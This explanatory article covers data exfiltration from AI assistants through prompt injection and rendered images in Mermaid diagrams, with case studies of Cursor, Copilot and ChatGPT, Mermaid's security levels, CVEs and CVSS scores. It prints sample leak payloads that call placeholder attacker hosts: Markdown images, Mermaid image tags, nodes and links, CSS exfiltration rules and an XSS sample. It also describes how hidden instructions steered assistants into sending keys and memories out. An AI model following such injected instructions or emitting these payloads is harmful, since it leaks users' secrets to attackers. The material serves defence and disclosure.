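# Data leaks through Mermaid diagrams in AI assistants

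## How can drawing a diagram send private data to a stranger?

Mermaid is an open-source JavaScript library that turns a short text description into a diagram. Knut Sveidqvist created it to make documentation easier, because a programmer can correct a diagram by editing a few lines of text. Many AI assistants now use it to show flowcharts and other diagrams in their chat windows. In 2025, security researchers reported that this feature could leak private data from Cursor, an AI code editor, and Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office software. An attacker who got the assistant to read hidden instructions could make it produce a diagram containing a web address with the user's data in it. In Cursor, the data went to the attacker's server as soon as the diagram appeared, while in Copilot the user had to click on the diagram first.

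The attack works because web pages load images from whatever address they are given, and language models cannot reliably distinguish their user's instructions from other instructions they read. The attacker does not need to steal a password or break into a server.

### From text to picture

A working Mermaid diagram can be two lines long. Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE*, the post in which the security researcher Johann Rehberger described the Cursor leak on his blog, begins with this one:

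```
graph TD
   User --> Computer
```

The first line sets the graph to run from top to bottom. The second defines two nodes and joins them with an arrow. The user sees a box labeled "User" with an arrow pointing down to a box labeled "Computer". Mermaid's documentation calls the notation "Markdown-inspired". Markdown is a simple way to format text with punctuation marks (two asterisks on either side of a word make it bold), and most chat assistants write their answers in it.

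A language model produces only text, so it can write the two lines above but cannot draw the boxes. The application draws them with its renderer, the part that turns text or markup into what the user sees. The renderer also makes words bold, lays out tables and displays pictures, and it may have to contact another computer to get a picture.

### Instructions hidden in what the assistant reads

Suppose someone asks an assistant to summarise a hotel's web page. The application adds the page's text to the request and passes both to the model as one piece of text. A stranger has hidden a paragraph on the page, in white letters on a white background, telling AI assistants to find any password in the conversation and include it in their answer in a particular form. The user cannot see this paragraph, but the model reads it with the rest of the page and may follow its instructions.

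This is indirect prompt injection, in which an assistant follows instructions hidden in material it reads. Microsoft (2025) describes the injected text as something the model "misinterprets as legitimate instructions", and points out that a web page is only one possible carrier. The instructions can also be in an email, a shared document, a plain text file, or the data that a software tool returns. For a programmer's assistant such as Cursor, a comment in a source code file is enough.

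An injection by itself may do no harm. If the hidden paragraph only makes the assistant write its summary in rhyme, the attacker gains nothing. A leak requires three conditions at once, which security researchers now often call the "lethal trifecta", after Simon Willison's *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025). The assistant must have access to private data. It must be exposed to untrusted content, meaning text or images that an attacker can influence. And it must be able to communicate with the outside world in a way that can carry the data to the attacker.

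A case from January 2026 had all three. As Willison recounts it, a user of Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant, asked for a summary of recent mail. The inbox was the private data, and the untrusted content was a message from an attacker that contained instructions. The assistant followed them. The way out was an image address, which it used to submit material from dozens of other emails to a Google Form that the attacker controlled. Some of that material was financial, legal or medical.

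The attack fails if any one of the three conditions is removed, but some are harder to remove than others. An assistant that cannot see the user's files is of little use for working on them, and one that never reads outside text cannot summarise a web page or an incoming email. Its makers also cannot count on the model to ignore hostile instructions every time, because the same injection may fail on one attempt and succeed on the next, and attackers can keep rephrasing it. So, as Willison observes, vendors have usually dealt with such reports by blocking the route through which data leaves.

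### How a picture's address carries data out

The Markdown image leak, the method most relevant to Mermaid, predates the Mermaid reports. The assistant writes an image address containing private data, and the application sends that data out when it requests the image. Moving private data to a party who should not have it is called exfiltration.

It works because a web address can hold more than the location of a page or file. It may also carry extra values after a question mark, such as search terms. Requesting the address sends those values to the server, and servers commonly keep a record of requests. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes how an attacker can trick a model into loading an address containing private data, then read the data in the server's log.

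Back to the hotel page, with a made-up secret. Earlier in the conversation the user mentioned that a password was "blue heron 42". The hidden paragraph tells the assistant to end its summary with a small picture and to put any password it has seen at the end of the picture's address. The assistant obeys and writes:

```
![logo](https://attacker.example/dot.png?d=blue%20heron%2042)
```

In Markdown, an exclamation mark followed by square brackets and round brackets displays an image. The square brackets hold a description and the round brackets hold the address. Each `%20` stands for a space, since web addresses cannot contain spaces. The server name is fictitious, because *Reserved Top Level DNS Names* (Eastlake and Panitz, 1999) set aside the ending ".example" for documentation so that no real site can own it.

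The renderer now converts the line into the HTML code for an image, and the user's browser, which has to get the picture from somewhere, connects to attacker.example and asks for it. The server replies with a transparent dot. At the same moment it adds a line to its log, which in the standard format that Apache, a widely used web server, can write would look like this:

```
203.0.113.7 - - [07/Oct/2026:10:15:32 +0000] "GET /dot.png?d=blue%20heron%2042 HTTP/1.1" 200 68
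```

The first number is the internet address of the machine that made the request, and the date and time follow it. The text between the quotation marks is the request itself, which includes the password. The last two numbers show that the server answered successfully (200) and sent 68 bytes. If the picture had not existed, the log would have shown the error code 404 instead of 200, but it would still have contained the password. The attacker returns an invisible dot only because a broken-image icon might make the user suspicious.

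Roman Samoilenko, in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, gave one of the first public demonstrations of this, which Willison (2023) shared with his readers that April. In Samoilenko's attack, a script on a web page added instructions to any text the visitor copied, and the visitor then pasted both into ChatGPT. In one test, ChatGPT corrected a short login function and then wrote an image address containing the whole function, including the password "123456". Another version told ChatGPT to attach an invisible image to every later answer, which sent each new question the user typed to Samoilenko's server.

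He acknowledged that the method was unreliable. The model's answers varied from one run to the next, and prompts that had worked sometimes stopped working. Code and earlier questions came out easily, but he found passwords and API keys (codes that programs use to identify themselves to online services) very difficult to extract. Rehberger, who found the same weakness that spring in Microsoft's Bing Chat, did extract a secret in a test. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* includes the instructions he planted on a web page. They told the assistant to wait for two turns, then write an image address containing a 200-character summary of the page and the chat, along with any passwords or secrets on the page. His server received the summary with the test secret in it.

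### With a click and without one

Samoilenko also tried a variant with no picture, in which ChatGPT wrote an ordinary link whose address contained the user's code. The address carried the data in both versions, but in this one the data went out only if the user followed the link.

A zero-click leak happens when the output is displayed, without the user clicking anything in it. A one-click leak happens only if the user clicks a link or button in the output. Microsoft makes the same distinction between images, which send the data out "without any user interaction", and links, which the user must click.

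A "zero-click" attack requires no click on the assistant's answer, though the user may still have to ask a question. *EchoLeak* (2025), a paper on an earlier attack against Microsoft 365 Copilot that did not involve diagrams, applies the term to images that the application fetches automatically. The attacker emailed instructions to the victim, who still had to ask Copilot an innocent question that led it to retrieve the email. Similarly, a Cursor user has to ask for a file to be explained before anything hidden in the file can take effect. In both cases, the application has already sent the request by the time the user has an answer to be careful with.

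With a one-click leak, the user may notice an odd address or lose interest and not click. This protection is limited because the text of a link can read "click here" while the address behind it carries the data. Some programs also remove the need for a click. Messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram show previews of the links in a message, and to build a preview the app has to request the page. PromptArmor, a security company, warns that when an assistant answers inside such an app, the preview makes the same kind of request as a click would, as soon as the message arrives. Whether a link is a one-click or a zero-click leak therefore depends partly on the program that displays it.

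### Why showing an answer is a network action

Data can leak from an assistant with no web tool (no ability to search or to open pages) because the application displaying the model's output can send requests, even though the model cannot. In the hotel example, the model only wrote a line of text. The renderer treated that line as a request for a picture, and the browser sent the request from the user's own machine. Turning off web search would not have stopped the leak, and neither would requiring the assistant to ask permission before using a tool, because the model didn't use one.

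*Trust No AI* (Rehberger, 2024) treats automatic images, link previews and clickable links as separate ways for data to leak, apart from anything an assistant does with its tools. It lists eleven products in which Rehberger had found and reported the image leak, including ChatGPT, Claude, Google Bard and GitHub Copilot Chat. OWASP, a non-profit that catalogues software security risks, uses an image leak as its example of indirect injection in *LLM01:2025 Prompt Injection*. In that example, a user asks for a summary of a web page, and the model inserts an image that leaks the conversation.

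The person whose screen sends the request may not be the person who was talking to the assistant. Red Hot Cyber's *OpenAI API Logs Vulnerability Exposed* (2026) reports PromptArmor's claim that data could leak through the page where developers review their chatbots' past answers. Even if a chatbot withheld a suspicious answer from its user, the data could escape when a developer later opened the logs, because the log page displayed Markdown images. Something similar happened in May 2026 with Copilot Cowork, a Microsoft assistant that could send emails to its user's own inbox without asking. Willison notes that these emails could contain external images, and that opening such an email sent the request.

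Loading an image can reveal information about the user even when the image's address contains no secret. In the same month, The Hacker News (2026) reported research by Permiso Security, which found that ChatGPT fetched images from pages it had summarised as soon as it displayed the answer. This gave the site's owner the user's internet address and browser type. That is far less serious than losing a password, but it shows that displaying an answer could still contact an outside server three years after Samoilenko's demonstration. Meanwhile, vendors have made it harder to leak secrets through image addresses. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* calls OpenAI's newer checks on addresses a significant improvement, though "not a solved problem".

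By 2025, the danger of loading images from outside servers in chat answers was well known, and many vendors had taken steps against it. Mermaid diagrams appeared in the same chat windows but used their own notation and drawing code. When Rehberger noticed that Cursor could draw them, he tested whether a diagram could include an image from another server, and Cursor fetched the image.

Rehberger also noticed that a diagram hides the leak better than the older trick did. Samoilenko had warned that users might notice the older attack if the answer appeared slowly, because they could watch a long, strange address being typed out. In Cursor, Rehberger wrote, "the diagram just appears", so the user has no chance to see the data being sent. His test raised the question of whether products that block outside pictures in ordinary text also block them inside Mermaid diagrams.

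## Which parts of a Mermaid diagram can contact another server?

A Mermaid diagram can make a browser contact another server through an image tag in a label, an image node, a link or a style rule. Images and style rules can cause zero-click leaks, and links can cause one-click leaks. Mermaid's security level partly determines which of these work in a given application. This setting controls how the library cleans diagram text and whether links and scripts work. At the default level, "strict", Mermaid is supposed to turn HTML tags into harmless text, but its final cleaning step targets scripts and lets image addresses through.

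### From diagram text to a drawing on the page

The source code of Mermaid 11.0.0 shows the order in which the library works. An application passes it some text, such as this:

```
flowchart TD
   A[Start] --> B[Finish]
```

Diagram text can include settings for colours, fonts and other styling, so whoever writes the text has some control over how Mermaid draws the diagram. Mermaid first separates any settings from the diagram itself. If the text is longer than the limit, normally 50,000 characters, Mermaid draws an error message instead.

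Next, Mermaid adds an empty, temporary SVG drawing to the page the user has open. SVG is a format that describes a picture as lines, shapes and text, and browsers can display it as part of a page. Mermaid then parses the diagram text, here a flowchart with two nodes and an arrow. It writes the style rules into the drawing and adds the nodes and their labels. The code for each type of diagram is supposed to clean the labels before it draws them.

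Mermaid reads the finished drawing back as text. At two of the four security levels, it passes this text through DOMPurify, a widely used sanitiser (code that removes or neutralises dangerous markup). Mermaid then deletes the temporary drawing and returns the text to the application, which inserts it into the page. Mintlify's *Rendering options*, a third-party guide to Mermaid, shows this last step as one line of code that assigns the text to `innerHTML`, the browser property that turns a string into page elements.

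Requests can start when Mermaid makes the temporary drawing and when the application inserts the finished one. DOMPurify runs between these two steps. Browsers generally begin fetching an image as soon as a page creates an image element with an address, so even if DOMPurify removed every image, it could be too late to stop a request from the temporary drawing. To prevent that request, Mermaid has to clean the label before drawing it.

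### Image tags in labels

Most labels are plain words, but Mermaid can also use HTML to draw them. Mintlify's *Mermaid config* lists the setting that controls this, `htmlLabels`. The HTML goes into a `foreignObject`, an SVG element made to hold content from outside SVG. It allows a label to contain bold text, or an image:

```
flowchart TD
   A["<img src='https://collector.example/dot.png?d=blue%20heron%2042' />"] --> B[Finish]
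```

If this tag reaches the page as working HTML, it leaks the made-up password from the hotel example without a click. Embrace The Red's demonstration against Cursor used a label of this form. Reef reported in *GHSA-w95v-4h65-j455* that SiYuan, a note-taking program set to Mermaid's loose level, also fetched the image when the user opened the note.

A sanitiser can work exactly as intended and still leave this route open. One of DOMPurify's own examples, which Socket reproduces, begins with an image tag that also contains a script to run if the picture fails to load:

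```
before:  <img src=x onerror=alert(1)//>
after:   <img src="x">
```

DOMPurify removed the script and kept the image and its address. This suits most websites, which want to show pictures without running a stranger's code.

### Image nodes

Since version 11.3.0, a flowchart node can also be a picture without any HTML in its label:

```
flowchart TD
   A@{ img: "https://collector.example/dot.png?d=blue%20heron%2042", label: "Logo", w: 60, h: 60 }
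```

This is also a zero-click route. Unlike the image tag, it puts no HTML in the label, so a filter that looks for HTML tags there will miss it. Mermaid defines its security levels in terms of HTML tags, scripts and clicks, and describes none of them as blocking pictures from other servers.

### Hyperlinks and the click directive

The `click` directive attaches an action to a node. Here the action is to open a web page:

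```
flowchart TD
   A[Read the full report]
   click A href "https://collector.example/r?d=blue%20heron%2042"
```

The user sees a box labelled "Read the full report". This is a one-click leak, like an ordinary link in a chat answer.

A link can also carry a script. Snyk's *Exploiting diagram renderers* describes an attack on Dify, a platform for building chatbots, that used the same directive with an address beginning `javascript:`, which makes the browser run code instead of opening a page. The code ran when a user clicked the node. This is cross-site scripting (XSS), a flaw that lets an attacker's script run inside a trusted page. Unlike a link with one secret in its address, such a script can read other parts of the page and send its own requests. Dify's developers fixed the flaw by changing the security level from loose to strict.

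The effect of strict on an ordinary web link is less clear. Mermaid's maintainers write that this level disables "click functionality", but the click directive can either open an address or call a JavaScript function that the application provides. In *Add config option to control mermaid securityLevel*, a post on the forum of the note-taking program Joplin, a user reported that Joplin kept Mermaid at strict. The user also gave an example of a diagram whose nodes linked to other notes, and wrote that Joplin seemed to support it. If so, strict blocked functions but left at least some links working.

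One forum post that does not name a Mermaid version is weak evidence, but the code of Mermaid 11.0.0 is consistent with it. The options that Mermaid passes to DOMPurify for the final cleaning do not forbid links. Developers who want diagrams without working links should therefore test whether links work, even at the default security level.

### Styling that disguises and styling that loads

CSS is the language that sets the colours, fonts and layout of a web page. A diagram can include styling of its own, for example through `classDef`, which gives a name to a set of styles:

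```
flowchart TD
   A[Log in]:::button
   classDef button fill:#2563eb,color:#ffffff,stroke:#1e40af
```

This produces a blue box with white text that looks like a button. The colours don't contact a server, but they may lead someone to click a link attached to the box, as the fake login button in Microsoft 365 Copilot did. The link carries the data, and the leak still takes one click.

Other CSS does load things. A rule can give an element a background picture from a web address:

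```
.label { background-image: url("https://collector.example/dot.png?d=blue%20heron%2042"); }
```

The browser requests the picture when it displays an element that this rule applies to. If a diagram can get such a rule onto the page, it causes a zero-click leak without an image tag, image node or link.

CSS can also extract data that the assistant never wrote into an address. GitHub Security Lab, the security research team of the code-hosting company GitHub, explained the method in a 2022 report on a Mermaid flaw. The attacker writes many rules, each of which applies only if a hidden value on the page begins with certain letters. Adapted to a harmless domain, two of them look like this:

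```
input[name=secret][value^=g]  { background-image: url("https://collector.example/?char=g"); }
input[name=secret][value^=go] { background-image: url("https://collector.example/?char=go"); }
```

If the value is "goose", the first rule applies and the browser requests the address ending in "g". The attacker then knows the first letter and can use further rules to find the rest. This method can read attributes in the page's code, such as the value of a form field, but not the ordinary text of a conversation. It also requires the attacker's CSS to affect the page outside the diagram. To prevent this, Mermaid attaches the diagram's identifier to each rule.

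Mermaid 11.0.0 inserts three styling settings, `themeCSS`, `fontFamily` and `altFontFamily`, into its CSS rules unchanged. In a comment beside that code, a developer tells contributors to clean such values with the project's CSS sanitising function, then writes "TODO where is this method?" Mermaid may do some cleaning earlier, but flaws recorded in 2026 involved all three settings.

### The four security levels

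Mermaid's configuration reference defines four values for `securityLevel`:

- **strict**, the default, encodes HTML tags and disables click functionality. Encoding replaces the characters that mark a tag, so that the browser shows the tag as text.
- **antiscript** allows HTML tags other than script elements, and enables clicks.
- **loose** allows HTML tags and enables clicks.
- **sandbox** draws the diagram inside an iframe, a separate page embedded in the main one, with JavaScript turned off.

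Mermaid's "strict" security level became the default in version 8.2, according to the documentation shipped with version 11.0.0. Application developers can choose another level, as the developers of SiYuan and Dify did.

In the 11.0.0 code, Mermaid runs a final DOMPurify pass at the strict and antiscript security levels. It skips this pass at loose, where HTML is meant to work, and at sandbox, where it relies on the iframe.

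Mermaid's sandbox level gives strong protection against scripts, but it does not fully isolate the diagram. The iframe's settings let it open new windows and let a user's click move the whole page to another address. Mermaid's maintainers warn that links may not work properly at this level, but the settings do not block them. The sandbox also does not stop images from loading. If an image tag or a style rule that loads a file survives earlier cleaning, the browser can still make the request from inside the iframe.

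### Does the default level stop outside images?

Mermaid's definition of the strict level implies that it blocks images in labels. If strict encodes every HTML tag, an image tag will appear as text and load nothing. The Joplin user understood it that way, and asked for the antiscript level because strict ruled out HTML images in nodes. Reef also recommended strict as the fix for SiYuan. For developers who needed HTML labels, he suggested a second DOMPurify pass that would remove images or allow only approved addresses.

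The code provides less assurance than the definition. In version 11.0.0, the options for the final DOMPurify pass permit `foreignobject` and one attribute for positioning text, and forbid nothing. An image that reaches this step can keep its address, as it does in DOMPurify's own example. Mermaid's maintainers also need HTML to remain after this step. They barred DOMPurify 3.1.7, which began to reject HTML inside SVG drawings, because it broke many diagrams. Newer code that Mintlify quotes configures DOMPurify to allow HTML inside `foreignobject`.

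The protection depends on how shared functions clean the label before Mermaid draws it. In the published declarations for 11.13.0, Mermaid's developers describe one of these functions, `removeScript`, as removing script tags, but they describe none as removing images.

Mintlify's configuration guide defines strict differently, as a level that allows "only safe elements and attributes". Encoding would turn an image tag into text, but a filter for safe elements could leave it working, because DOMPurify accepts images. Mintlify did not write Mermaid, and its other guide repeats Mermaid's "encoded" wording, so its account is not enough to establish which definition is correct.

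In version 11.0.0, the final cleaning at the default level, strict, removes scripts but not remote images, so only the earlier encoding can block image tags in labels. Developers should test whether strict blocks images before relying on it, for example by drawing a label with an image from a server they control and watching for the request. In 2025, researchers reported two kinds of diagram text that reached the page uncleaned in Mermaid's default configuration.

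### Flaws recorded in Mermaid itself

Both of the 2025 flaws allowed cross-site scripting. Corgea's *Mermaid improperly sanitizes sequence diagram labels leading to XSS* describes one of them, CVE-2025-54881 (a CVE is a public identifier for a software vulnerability). Mermaid measures each label to lay out a diagram. When a label in a sequence diagram contained the marks that introduce a mathematical formula, version 11.9.0 put the whole label into the page to measure it, without cleaning it first. An attacker could therefore add any HTML, including an image tag with a script. GitHub's *GHSA-7rqq-prvp-x9jh* (2025) rates the flaw as moderate and lists 11.10.0 and 10.9.4 as the fixed versions.

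The other flaw, CVE-2025-54880, was in architecture diagrams, which show the parts of a computer system. These diagrams can use text as an icon, and Mermaid inserted that text as HTML. Corgea traces the mistake to version 11.1.0 and reproduces a test in which the icon text was an image tag with a script attached. GitHub's *GHSA-8gwm-58g9-j8pw* (2025) advises cleaning the icon text before inserting it. Mermaid's maintainers published both advisories on 19 August 2025.

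A flaw that lets an attacker insert an image tag with a script also lets the attacker insert one with only a remote address. The default security level in the affected versions therefore could not have fully blocked zero-click image requests, although neither advisory is about assistants leaking data.

Mermaid's developers had fixed related mistakes before. Acunetix's *CVE-2021-35513 Vulnerability in npm package mermaid* records cross-site scripting at the antiscript level in versions before 8.11.0. In 2021, GitHub Security Lab found that Mermaid's link cleaning could turn a deliberately jumbled address into a working `javascript:` address, and that Mermaid skipped part of the cleaning for links in sequence diagrams when an application turned HTML labels off. GitLab's *GHSA-m4gq-x24j-jpmf* (2024) warned that some prebuilt Mermaid files contained a vulnerable copy of the sanitiser DOMPurify,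 which might allow cross-site scripting.

The flaws recorded in 2026 mostly concern CSS. OSV's *CVE-2026-41148*, an entry in a database of open-source vulnerabilities, describes how a `classDef` value in a state diagram could contain a closing brace. The brace ended Mermaid's CSS rule, so the browser applied the text after it to the whole page as a new rule. An attacker could change the page's appearance, make the browser contact an outside server through `url()`, or extract HTML attributes. The developers fixed this in versions 10.9.6 and 11.15.0.

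The same two releases fixed CVE-2026-41149, another flaw in how state diagrams handled `classDef`. According to Red Hat's *Bug 2480864 (CVE-2026-41149)* (2026), the flaw let an attacker insert HTML outside the SVG drawing in the default configuration. Mermaid removed script tags, which prevented cross-site scripting but would not necessarily prevent a leak, since an image tag can send a request without a script.

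They also fixed CVE-2026-41159, which involved the three styling settings that Mermaid 11.0.0 copied into its CSS rules. *CVE-2026-41159* (2026), in the United States' National Vulnerability Database (NVD), confirms that the default configuration was affected. The example in OSV's *GHSA-87f9-hvmw-gh4p* shows how an attacker could apply CSS outside the diagram. In the tool that Mermaid uses to process styles, `&` stands for the diagram, so a rule for `:not(&)` applies to the rest of the page. The advisory warns that attackers could alter pages and steal attributes.

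A related flaw, CVE-2026-50159, let `themeCSS` style whatever came immediately after the diagram on the page. Docker's *CVE-2026-50159* advises developers who insert the drawing themselves to put it in its own container. Developers can also use Mermaid's `secure` setting to stop diagram text from changing the styling options, or choose the sandbox level. The sandbox keeps such CSS from affecting the rest of the page, but a rule inside the iframe could still load a background image.

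Mermaid's maintainers say in the project's introduction that standard cleaning breaks diagrams because they use many characters that also have a meaning in HTML. The maintainers say they keep improving their own cleaning, but "it is hard to guarantee that there are no loop holes".

The table compares the routes at each level, using Mermaid's definitions and the code of version 11.0.0. Mermaid added image nodes later, in version 11.3.0. "No stated block" means that Mermaid does not describe the level as blocking that route, so a developer would need to test it.

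| Route | Type of leak | strict (default) | antiscript | loose | sandbox |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| HTML image tag in a label | Zero-click | Should become text; final cleaning does not remove images | Allowed | Allowed | No stated block; the iframe does not stop images |
| Image node | Zero-click | No stated block | No stated block | No stated block | No stated block; the iframe does not stop images |
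| Link added with `click` | One-click | Clicks officially disabled; a Joplin user reported working links | Allowed | Allowed | May not work properly; the iframe permits new windows |
| CSS that disguises a link | None without a click on the link | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |
| CSS that loads a remote resource | Zero-click | No stated block | No stated block | No stated block | Cannot style the surrounding page; the iframe does not stop the request |

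## How did Cursor leak secrets, and why were two patches needed?

Cursor leaked secrets because its chat window drew Mermaid diagrams and fetched the images in them from outside servers without asking the user. In June 2025, Johann Rehberger reported that a comment in a source file could make the assistant put an API key into the address of such an image. Anysphere, which makes Cursor, released a fix in version 1.3 the following month. Researchers later found ways around it, and Anysphere released a second fix in version 1.7. GitHub issued CVE records for both flaws but did not describe in them what the first fix had missed.

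### From a code comment to an image request

Programmers often open code that strangers wrote, such as a sample project or a library from the internet, and may ask an assistant to explain it. Rehberger's attack relied on this. His test file was a short C program that printed "Hello, world!", with a comment above the code. Comments are text for human readers that the computer skips when it builds the program. Rehberger described the program in the first line of the comment, and used the rest to tell any assistant explaining the file what to put in its answer.

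The comment contained instructions to write a short greeting that named Rehberger, followed by a Mermaid diagram and a closing slogan. The greeting and slogan made it obvious that the assistant was following the comment, but they carried no data. The diagram had four nodes in a row, and the third node's label was an HTML image tag. The image's address led to Rehberger's server and ended in a placeholder for the stolen data. The assistant was to write that data as one sentence and encode it for use in a web address.

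Rehberger also told the assistant to avoid backslashes and double quotes in labels and to make sure that the Mermaid diagram was valid. Valid syntax matters to an attacker because Mermaid cannot draw a diagram that it cannot parse, and an image in the diagram loads only if the diagram is drawn.

He then asked Cursor to explain the file, using agent mode, in which the assistant can take several steps on its own, such as searching a project. The assistant read the comment, gathered the data and wrote the diagram text with the data in the image's address. When the chat window drew the diagram, it requested the image "without human confirmation", Rehberger wrote on Embrace The Red.

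At its default security level, Mermaid cleans labels, which should have turned the image tag into harmless text. The image loaded, so either Cursor used a looser level or the cleaning failed, but Rehberger did not say which.

### An API key and a set of memories

Rehberger sent Anysphere two demonstrations. One used an application built with Microsoft's .NET, with an API key in its configuration file, `app.config`, and the malicious comment in a separate source file. When Rehberger asked Cursor to analyse that source file, it searched the project for keys, found the one in `app.config` and drew a diagram with the key in the image's address. The key then arrived at his server.

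The user in this scenario never pasted the key into the chat or asked about the configuration file. Samoilenko's attack on ChatGPT worked on text that the user pasted, whereas Cursor's assistant could look for the key on its own.

In the other demonstration, Rehberger stole Cursor's memories, which are notes the assistant stores about the developer. He first gave Cursor some memories, then had it explain the "Hello, world!" program. Cursor retrieved the memories and put them into the image's address, and they appeared in his web server's log. An attacker could do this without knowing anything about the victim's project, just by writing a comment that requests whatever Cursor has stored.

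In both cases the diagram appeared already finished, so the user could not watch the address being written. Rehberger published screenshots and a video of the two attacks, but no figure for how often they worked. The demonstrations show that the leak was possible in the versions he tested, but not how reliably it would have worked with a different model or a differently worded question.

Rehberger used keys and memories as examples, but he warned that an attacker could take anything the assistant could be made to bring into the conversation. He also mentioned Slack messages and tickets from the work-tracking program Jira, both of which Cursor could reach through MCP servers (small programs that connect an assistant to other services).

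He added that the leak might not need hidden instructions. A model with a deliberate backdoor could draw such a diagram at any time, and a model might even draw one by mistake. Teaching the model to distrust comments in source files would not prevent either of these.

### The first patch

Rehberger reported the flaw on 30 June 2025. Anysphere's developers had fixed it by 7 July, but they held the fix for their next major release, version 1.3, which came out on 29 July. Rehberger thanked them for acting promptly.

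GitHub reserved the number CVE-2025-54132 for this flaw on 16 July and published the record on 1 August. *Cursor's Mermaid Diagram Tool is Vulnerable to an Arbitrary Image Fetch* (2025), the entry in the official CVE list maintained by the American non-profit MITRE, lists every version of Cursor below 1.3 as affected. Rehberger announced his findings on 4 August in a social media post, which the security company Intruder reproduces.

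Users therefore had six days to update before he publicised the method. Anyone still on an older version after that was exposed to an attack with published instructions. A vulnerability tracker's entry, *CVE-2025-54132*, also lists a public proof of concept (code or instructions for reproducing an attack) on GitHub.

Users who did update had reason to think the problem was over, since GitHub had named version 1.3 as the fix. Microsoft also issued a notice for Visual Studio under the same CVE number.

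### The bypasses and the second patch

GitHub published a second record on 3 October 2025. According to MITRE's *CVE-2025-61589* (2025), it covers every version of Cursor before 1.7. GitHub's description repeats the first one almost word for word. An attacker uses prompt injection to embed an image in a diagram, and Cursor fetches the image when it draws the diagram in the chat. GitHub added a sentence about "additional bypasses not covered in the initial fix". Versions 1.3 to 1.6 were therefore still vulnerable, even with the first patch.

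That sentence ends by referring readers to the GitHub security advisory GHSA-43wj-mwcc-x93p, which MITRE lists as the source of the August record. This advisory is for the first flaw, the original leak, so the reference can mislead readers who want to learn about the bypasses. The second flaw has its own advisory, GHSA-xw2x-252g-97w2.

GitHub probably meant the reference to identify "the initial fix" rather than the bypasses. *CVE-2025-61589* (2025), a tracker entry that includes NVD's change history, shows that on 20 October NVD's analysts marked the older advisory "Not Applicable" and the newer one as the vendor's advisory.

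Ari Marzouk, a security researcher, was probably one of two people who reported the second flaw. Positive Technologies' *PT-2025-40459* (2025), an entry in the security company's vulnerability database, credits "Maccarita +1" without naming the other person, and The Hacker News (2025) identifies MaccariTA as Marzouk. By December 2025, he had disclosed more than 30 flaws in AI code editors, including Cursor, and their extensions.

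Positive Technologies credits the first flaw accurately, which is some reason to trust its credit for the second. Its *PT-2025-31700* (2025) names Wunderwuzzi23, the handle Rehberger uses on social media, and Rehberger says he received the official credit. GitHub's own entries list the discovery of both flaws as "unknown", even though Rehberger had described the first at length.

The exact gap in the first patch is not public. GitHub's records include neither the diagram text that got past the patch nor the change that Anysphere made in version 1.7. GitHub describes the leak as an "image fetch", so the gap was not simply a link that the user had to click. It also refers to "bypasses", so there was more than one.

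An image node could fit this description because it needs no HTML tag, and so could a style rule with a background picture or an unusual spelling of the image tag, but these are guesses. There were several bypasses, which suggests that the first patch blocked particular kinds of diagram text and still let Cursor contact outside servers, but Anysphere could have made a different mistake.

In version 1.7, Anysphere had to revisit the Mermaid fix and at least one other. *CVE-2025-61590*, an entry from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, INCIBE, describes a way around the fix for another flaw, CVE-2025-54130. An attacker who had taken over the chat could make the assistant write to a workspace file, which stores a project's settings, and could then use those settings to run code on the user's machine. According to a tracker's page on the Mermaid bypass, *CVE-2025-61589*, six Cursor vulnerabilities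 were published on 3 October.

### Why the first flaw scored both 4.4 and 7.5

A CVSS score rates the severity of a flaw from 0 to 10, using stated assumptions about how an attack would work. GitHub gave the first Cursor flaw 4.4 (medium), while NVD gave it 7.5 (high). GitHub then gave the second flaw 5.9.

In all three ratings, the attack comes over a network, needs no action by the user, reveals a great deal of private information, and does not alter data or stop the program from working. The ratings differ only in attack complexity and the privileges the attacker needs beforehand.

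| Rating | Attack complexity | Privileges required | Exploitability | Impact | Score |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| First flaw, GitHub | High | High | 0.7 | 3.6 | 4.4 |
| First flaw, NVD | Low | None | 3.9 | 3.6 | 7.5 |
| Second flaw, GitHub | High | None | 2.2 | 3.6 | 5.9 |

Exploitability measures how easy the attack is, and impact measures the damage if it succeeds. The sub-scores for GitHub's first rating come from *CVE-2025-54132*, an entry by CERT.hr, Croatia's national computer emergency team, and NVD's come from Intruder. The figure of 2.2 for the second flaw follows from the published formula. Impact is 3.6 in every row, so the ratings differ only in exploitability.

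Version 3.1 of CVSS, which GitHub and NVD both used, calculates exploitability by multiplying a constant by four weights. They stand for the attacker's position, the attack's complexity, the privileges required and the user's involvement:

```
First flaw, GitHub:   8.22 × 0.85 × 0.44 × 0.27 × 0.85 = 0.7055
First flaw, NVD:      8.22 × 0.85 × 0.77 × 0.85 × 0.85 = 3.8870
Second flaw, GitHub:  8.22 × 0.85 × 0.44 × 0.85 × 0.85 = 2.2212
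```

High complexity has a weight of 0.44 and low complexity 0.77. Requiring high privileges has a weight of 0.27, and requiring none 0.85. Adding the unrounded impact of 3.5952 gives totals of 4.3007, 7.4822 and 5.8164. CVSS always rounds up to one decimal place, so 4.3007 becomes 4.4.

The second flaw's rating of 5.9 happens to be midway between the other two. GitHub would have given the first flaw the same rating if it had assumed in August that the attacker needed no privileges. Also changing the complexity from high to low raises the rating to 7.5.

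GitHub's original assumption about privileges is hard to defend. In CVSS, a "high" privilege requirement means the attacker already has significant control over the vulnerable software, such as an administrator's rights. Rehberger's attacker needed no account in Cursor and no access to the victim's computer, only a file that the victim would ask the assistant to explain. GitHub listed web pages and uploaded images as possible sources of the injection. Two months later, it dropped the assumption, without giving a reason in the record, for an attack it described in nearly the same words.

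Both views of complexity are reasonable. CVSS treats an attack as highly complex when success depends on conditions the attacker does not control. Here the user has to bring the hostile text to the assistant, the model has to follow it, and the assistant has to have access to a secret worth stealing. On the other hand, an attacker can write one comment and place it in many files, and Rehberger's comment required no knowledge of the victim's machine. CVSS 3.1 has no separate setting for whether a model will follow an instruction, so scorers have to decide how to account for that uncertainty. GitHub seems to have counted it as complexity, while NVD seems not to have. A score of 5.9 or 7.5 is therefore defensible, but 4.4 is too low.

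All three ratings are also based on the attack needing no user action, although in both demonstrations someone had to ask Cursor about the file. A stricter scorer could count that question as user action, which would lower NVD's rating from 7.5 to 6.5.

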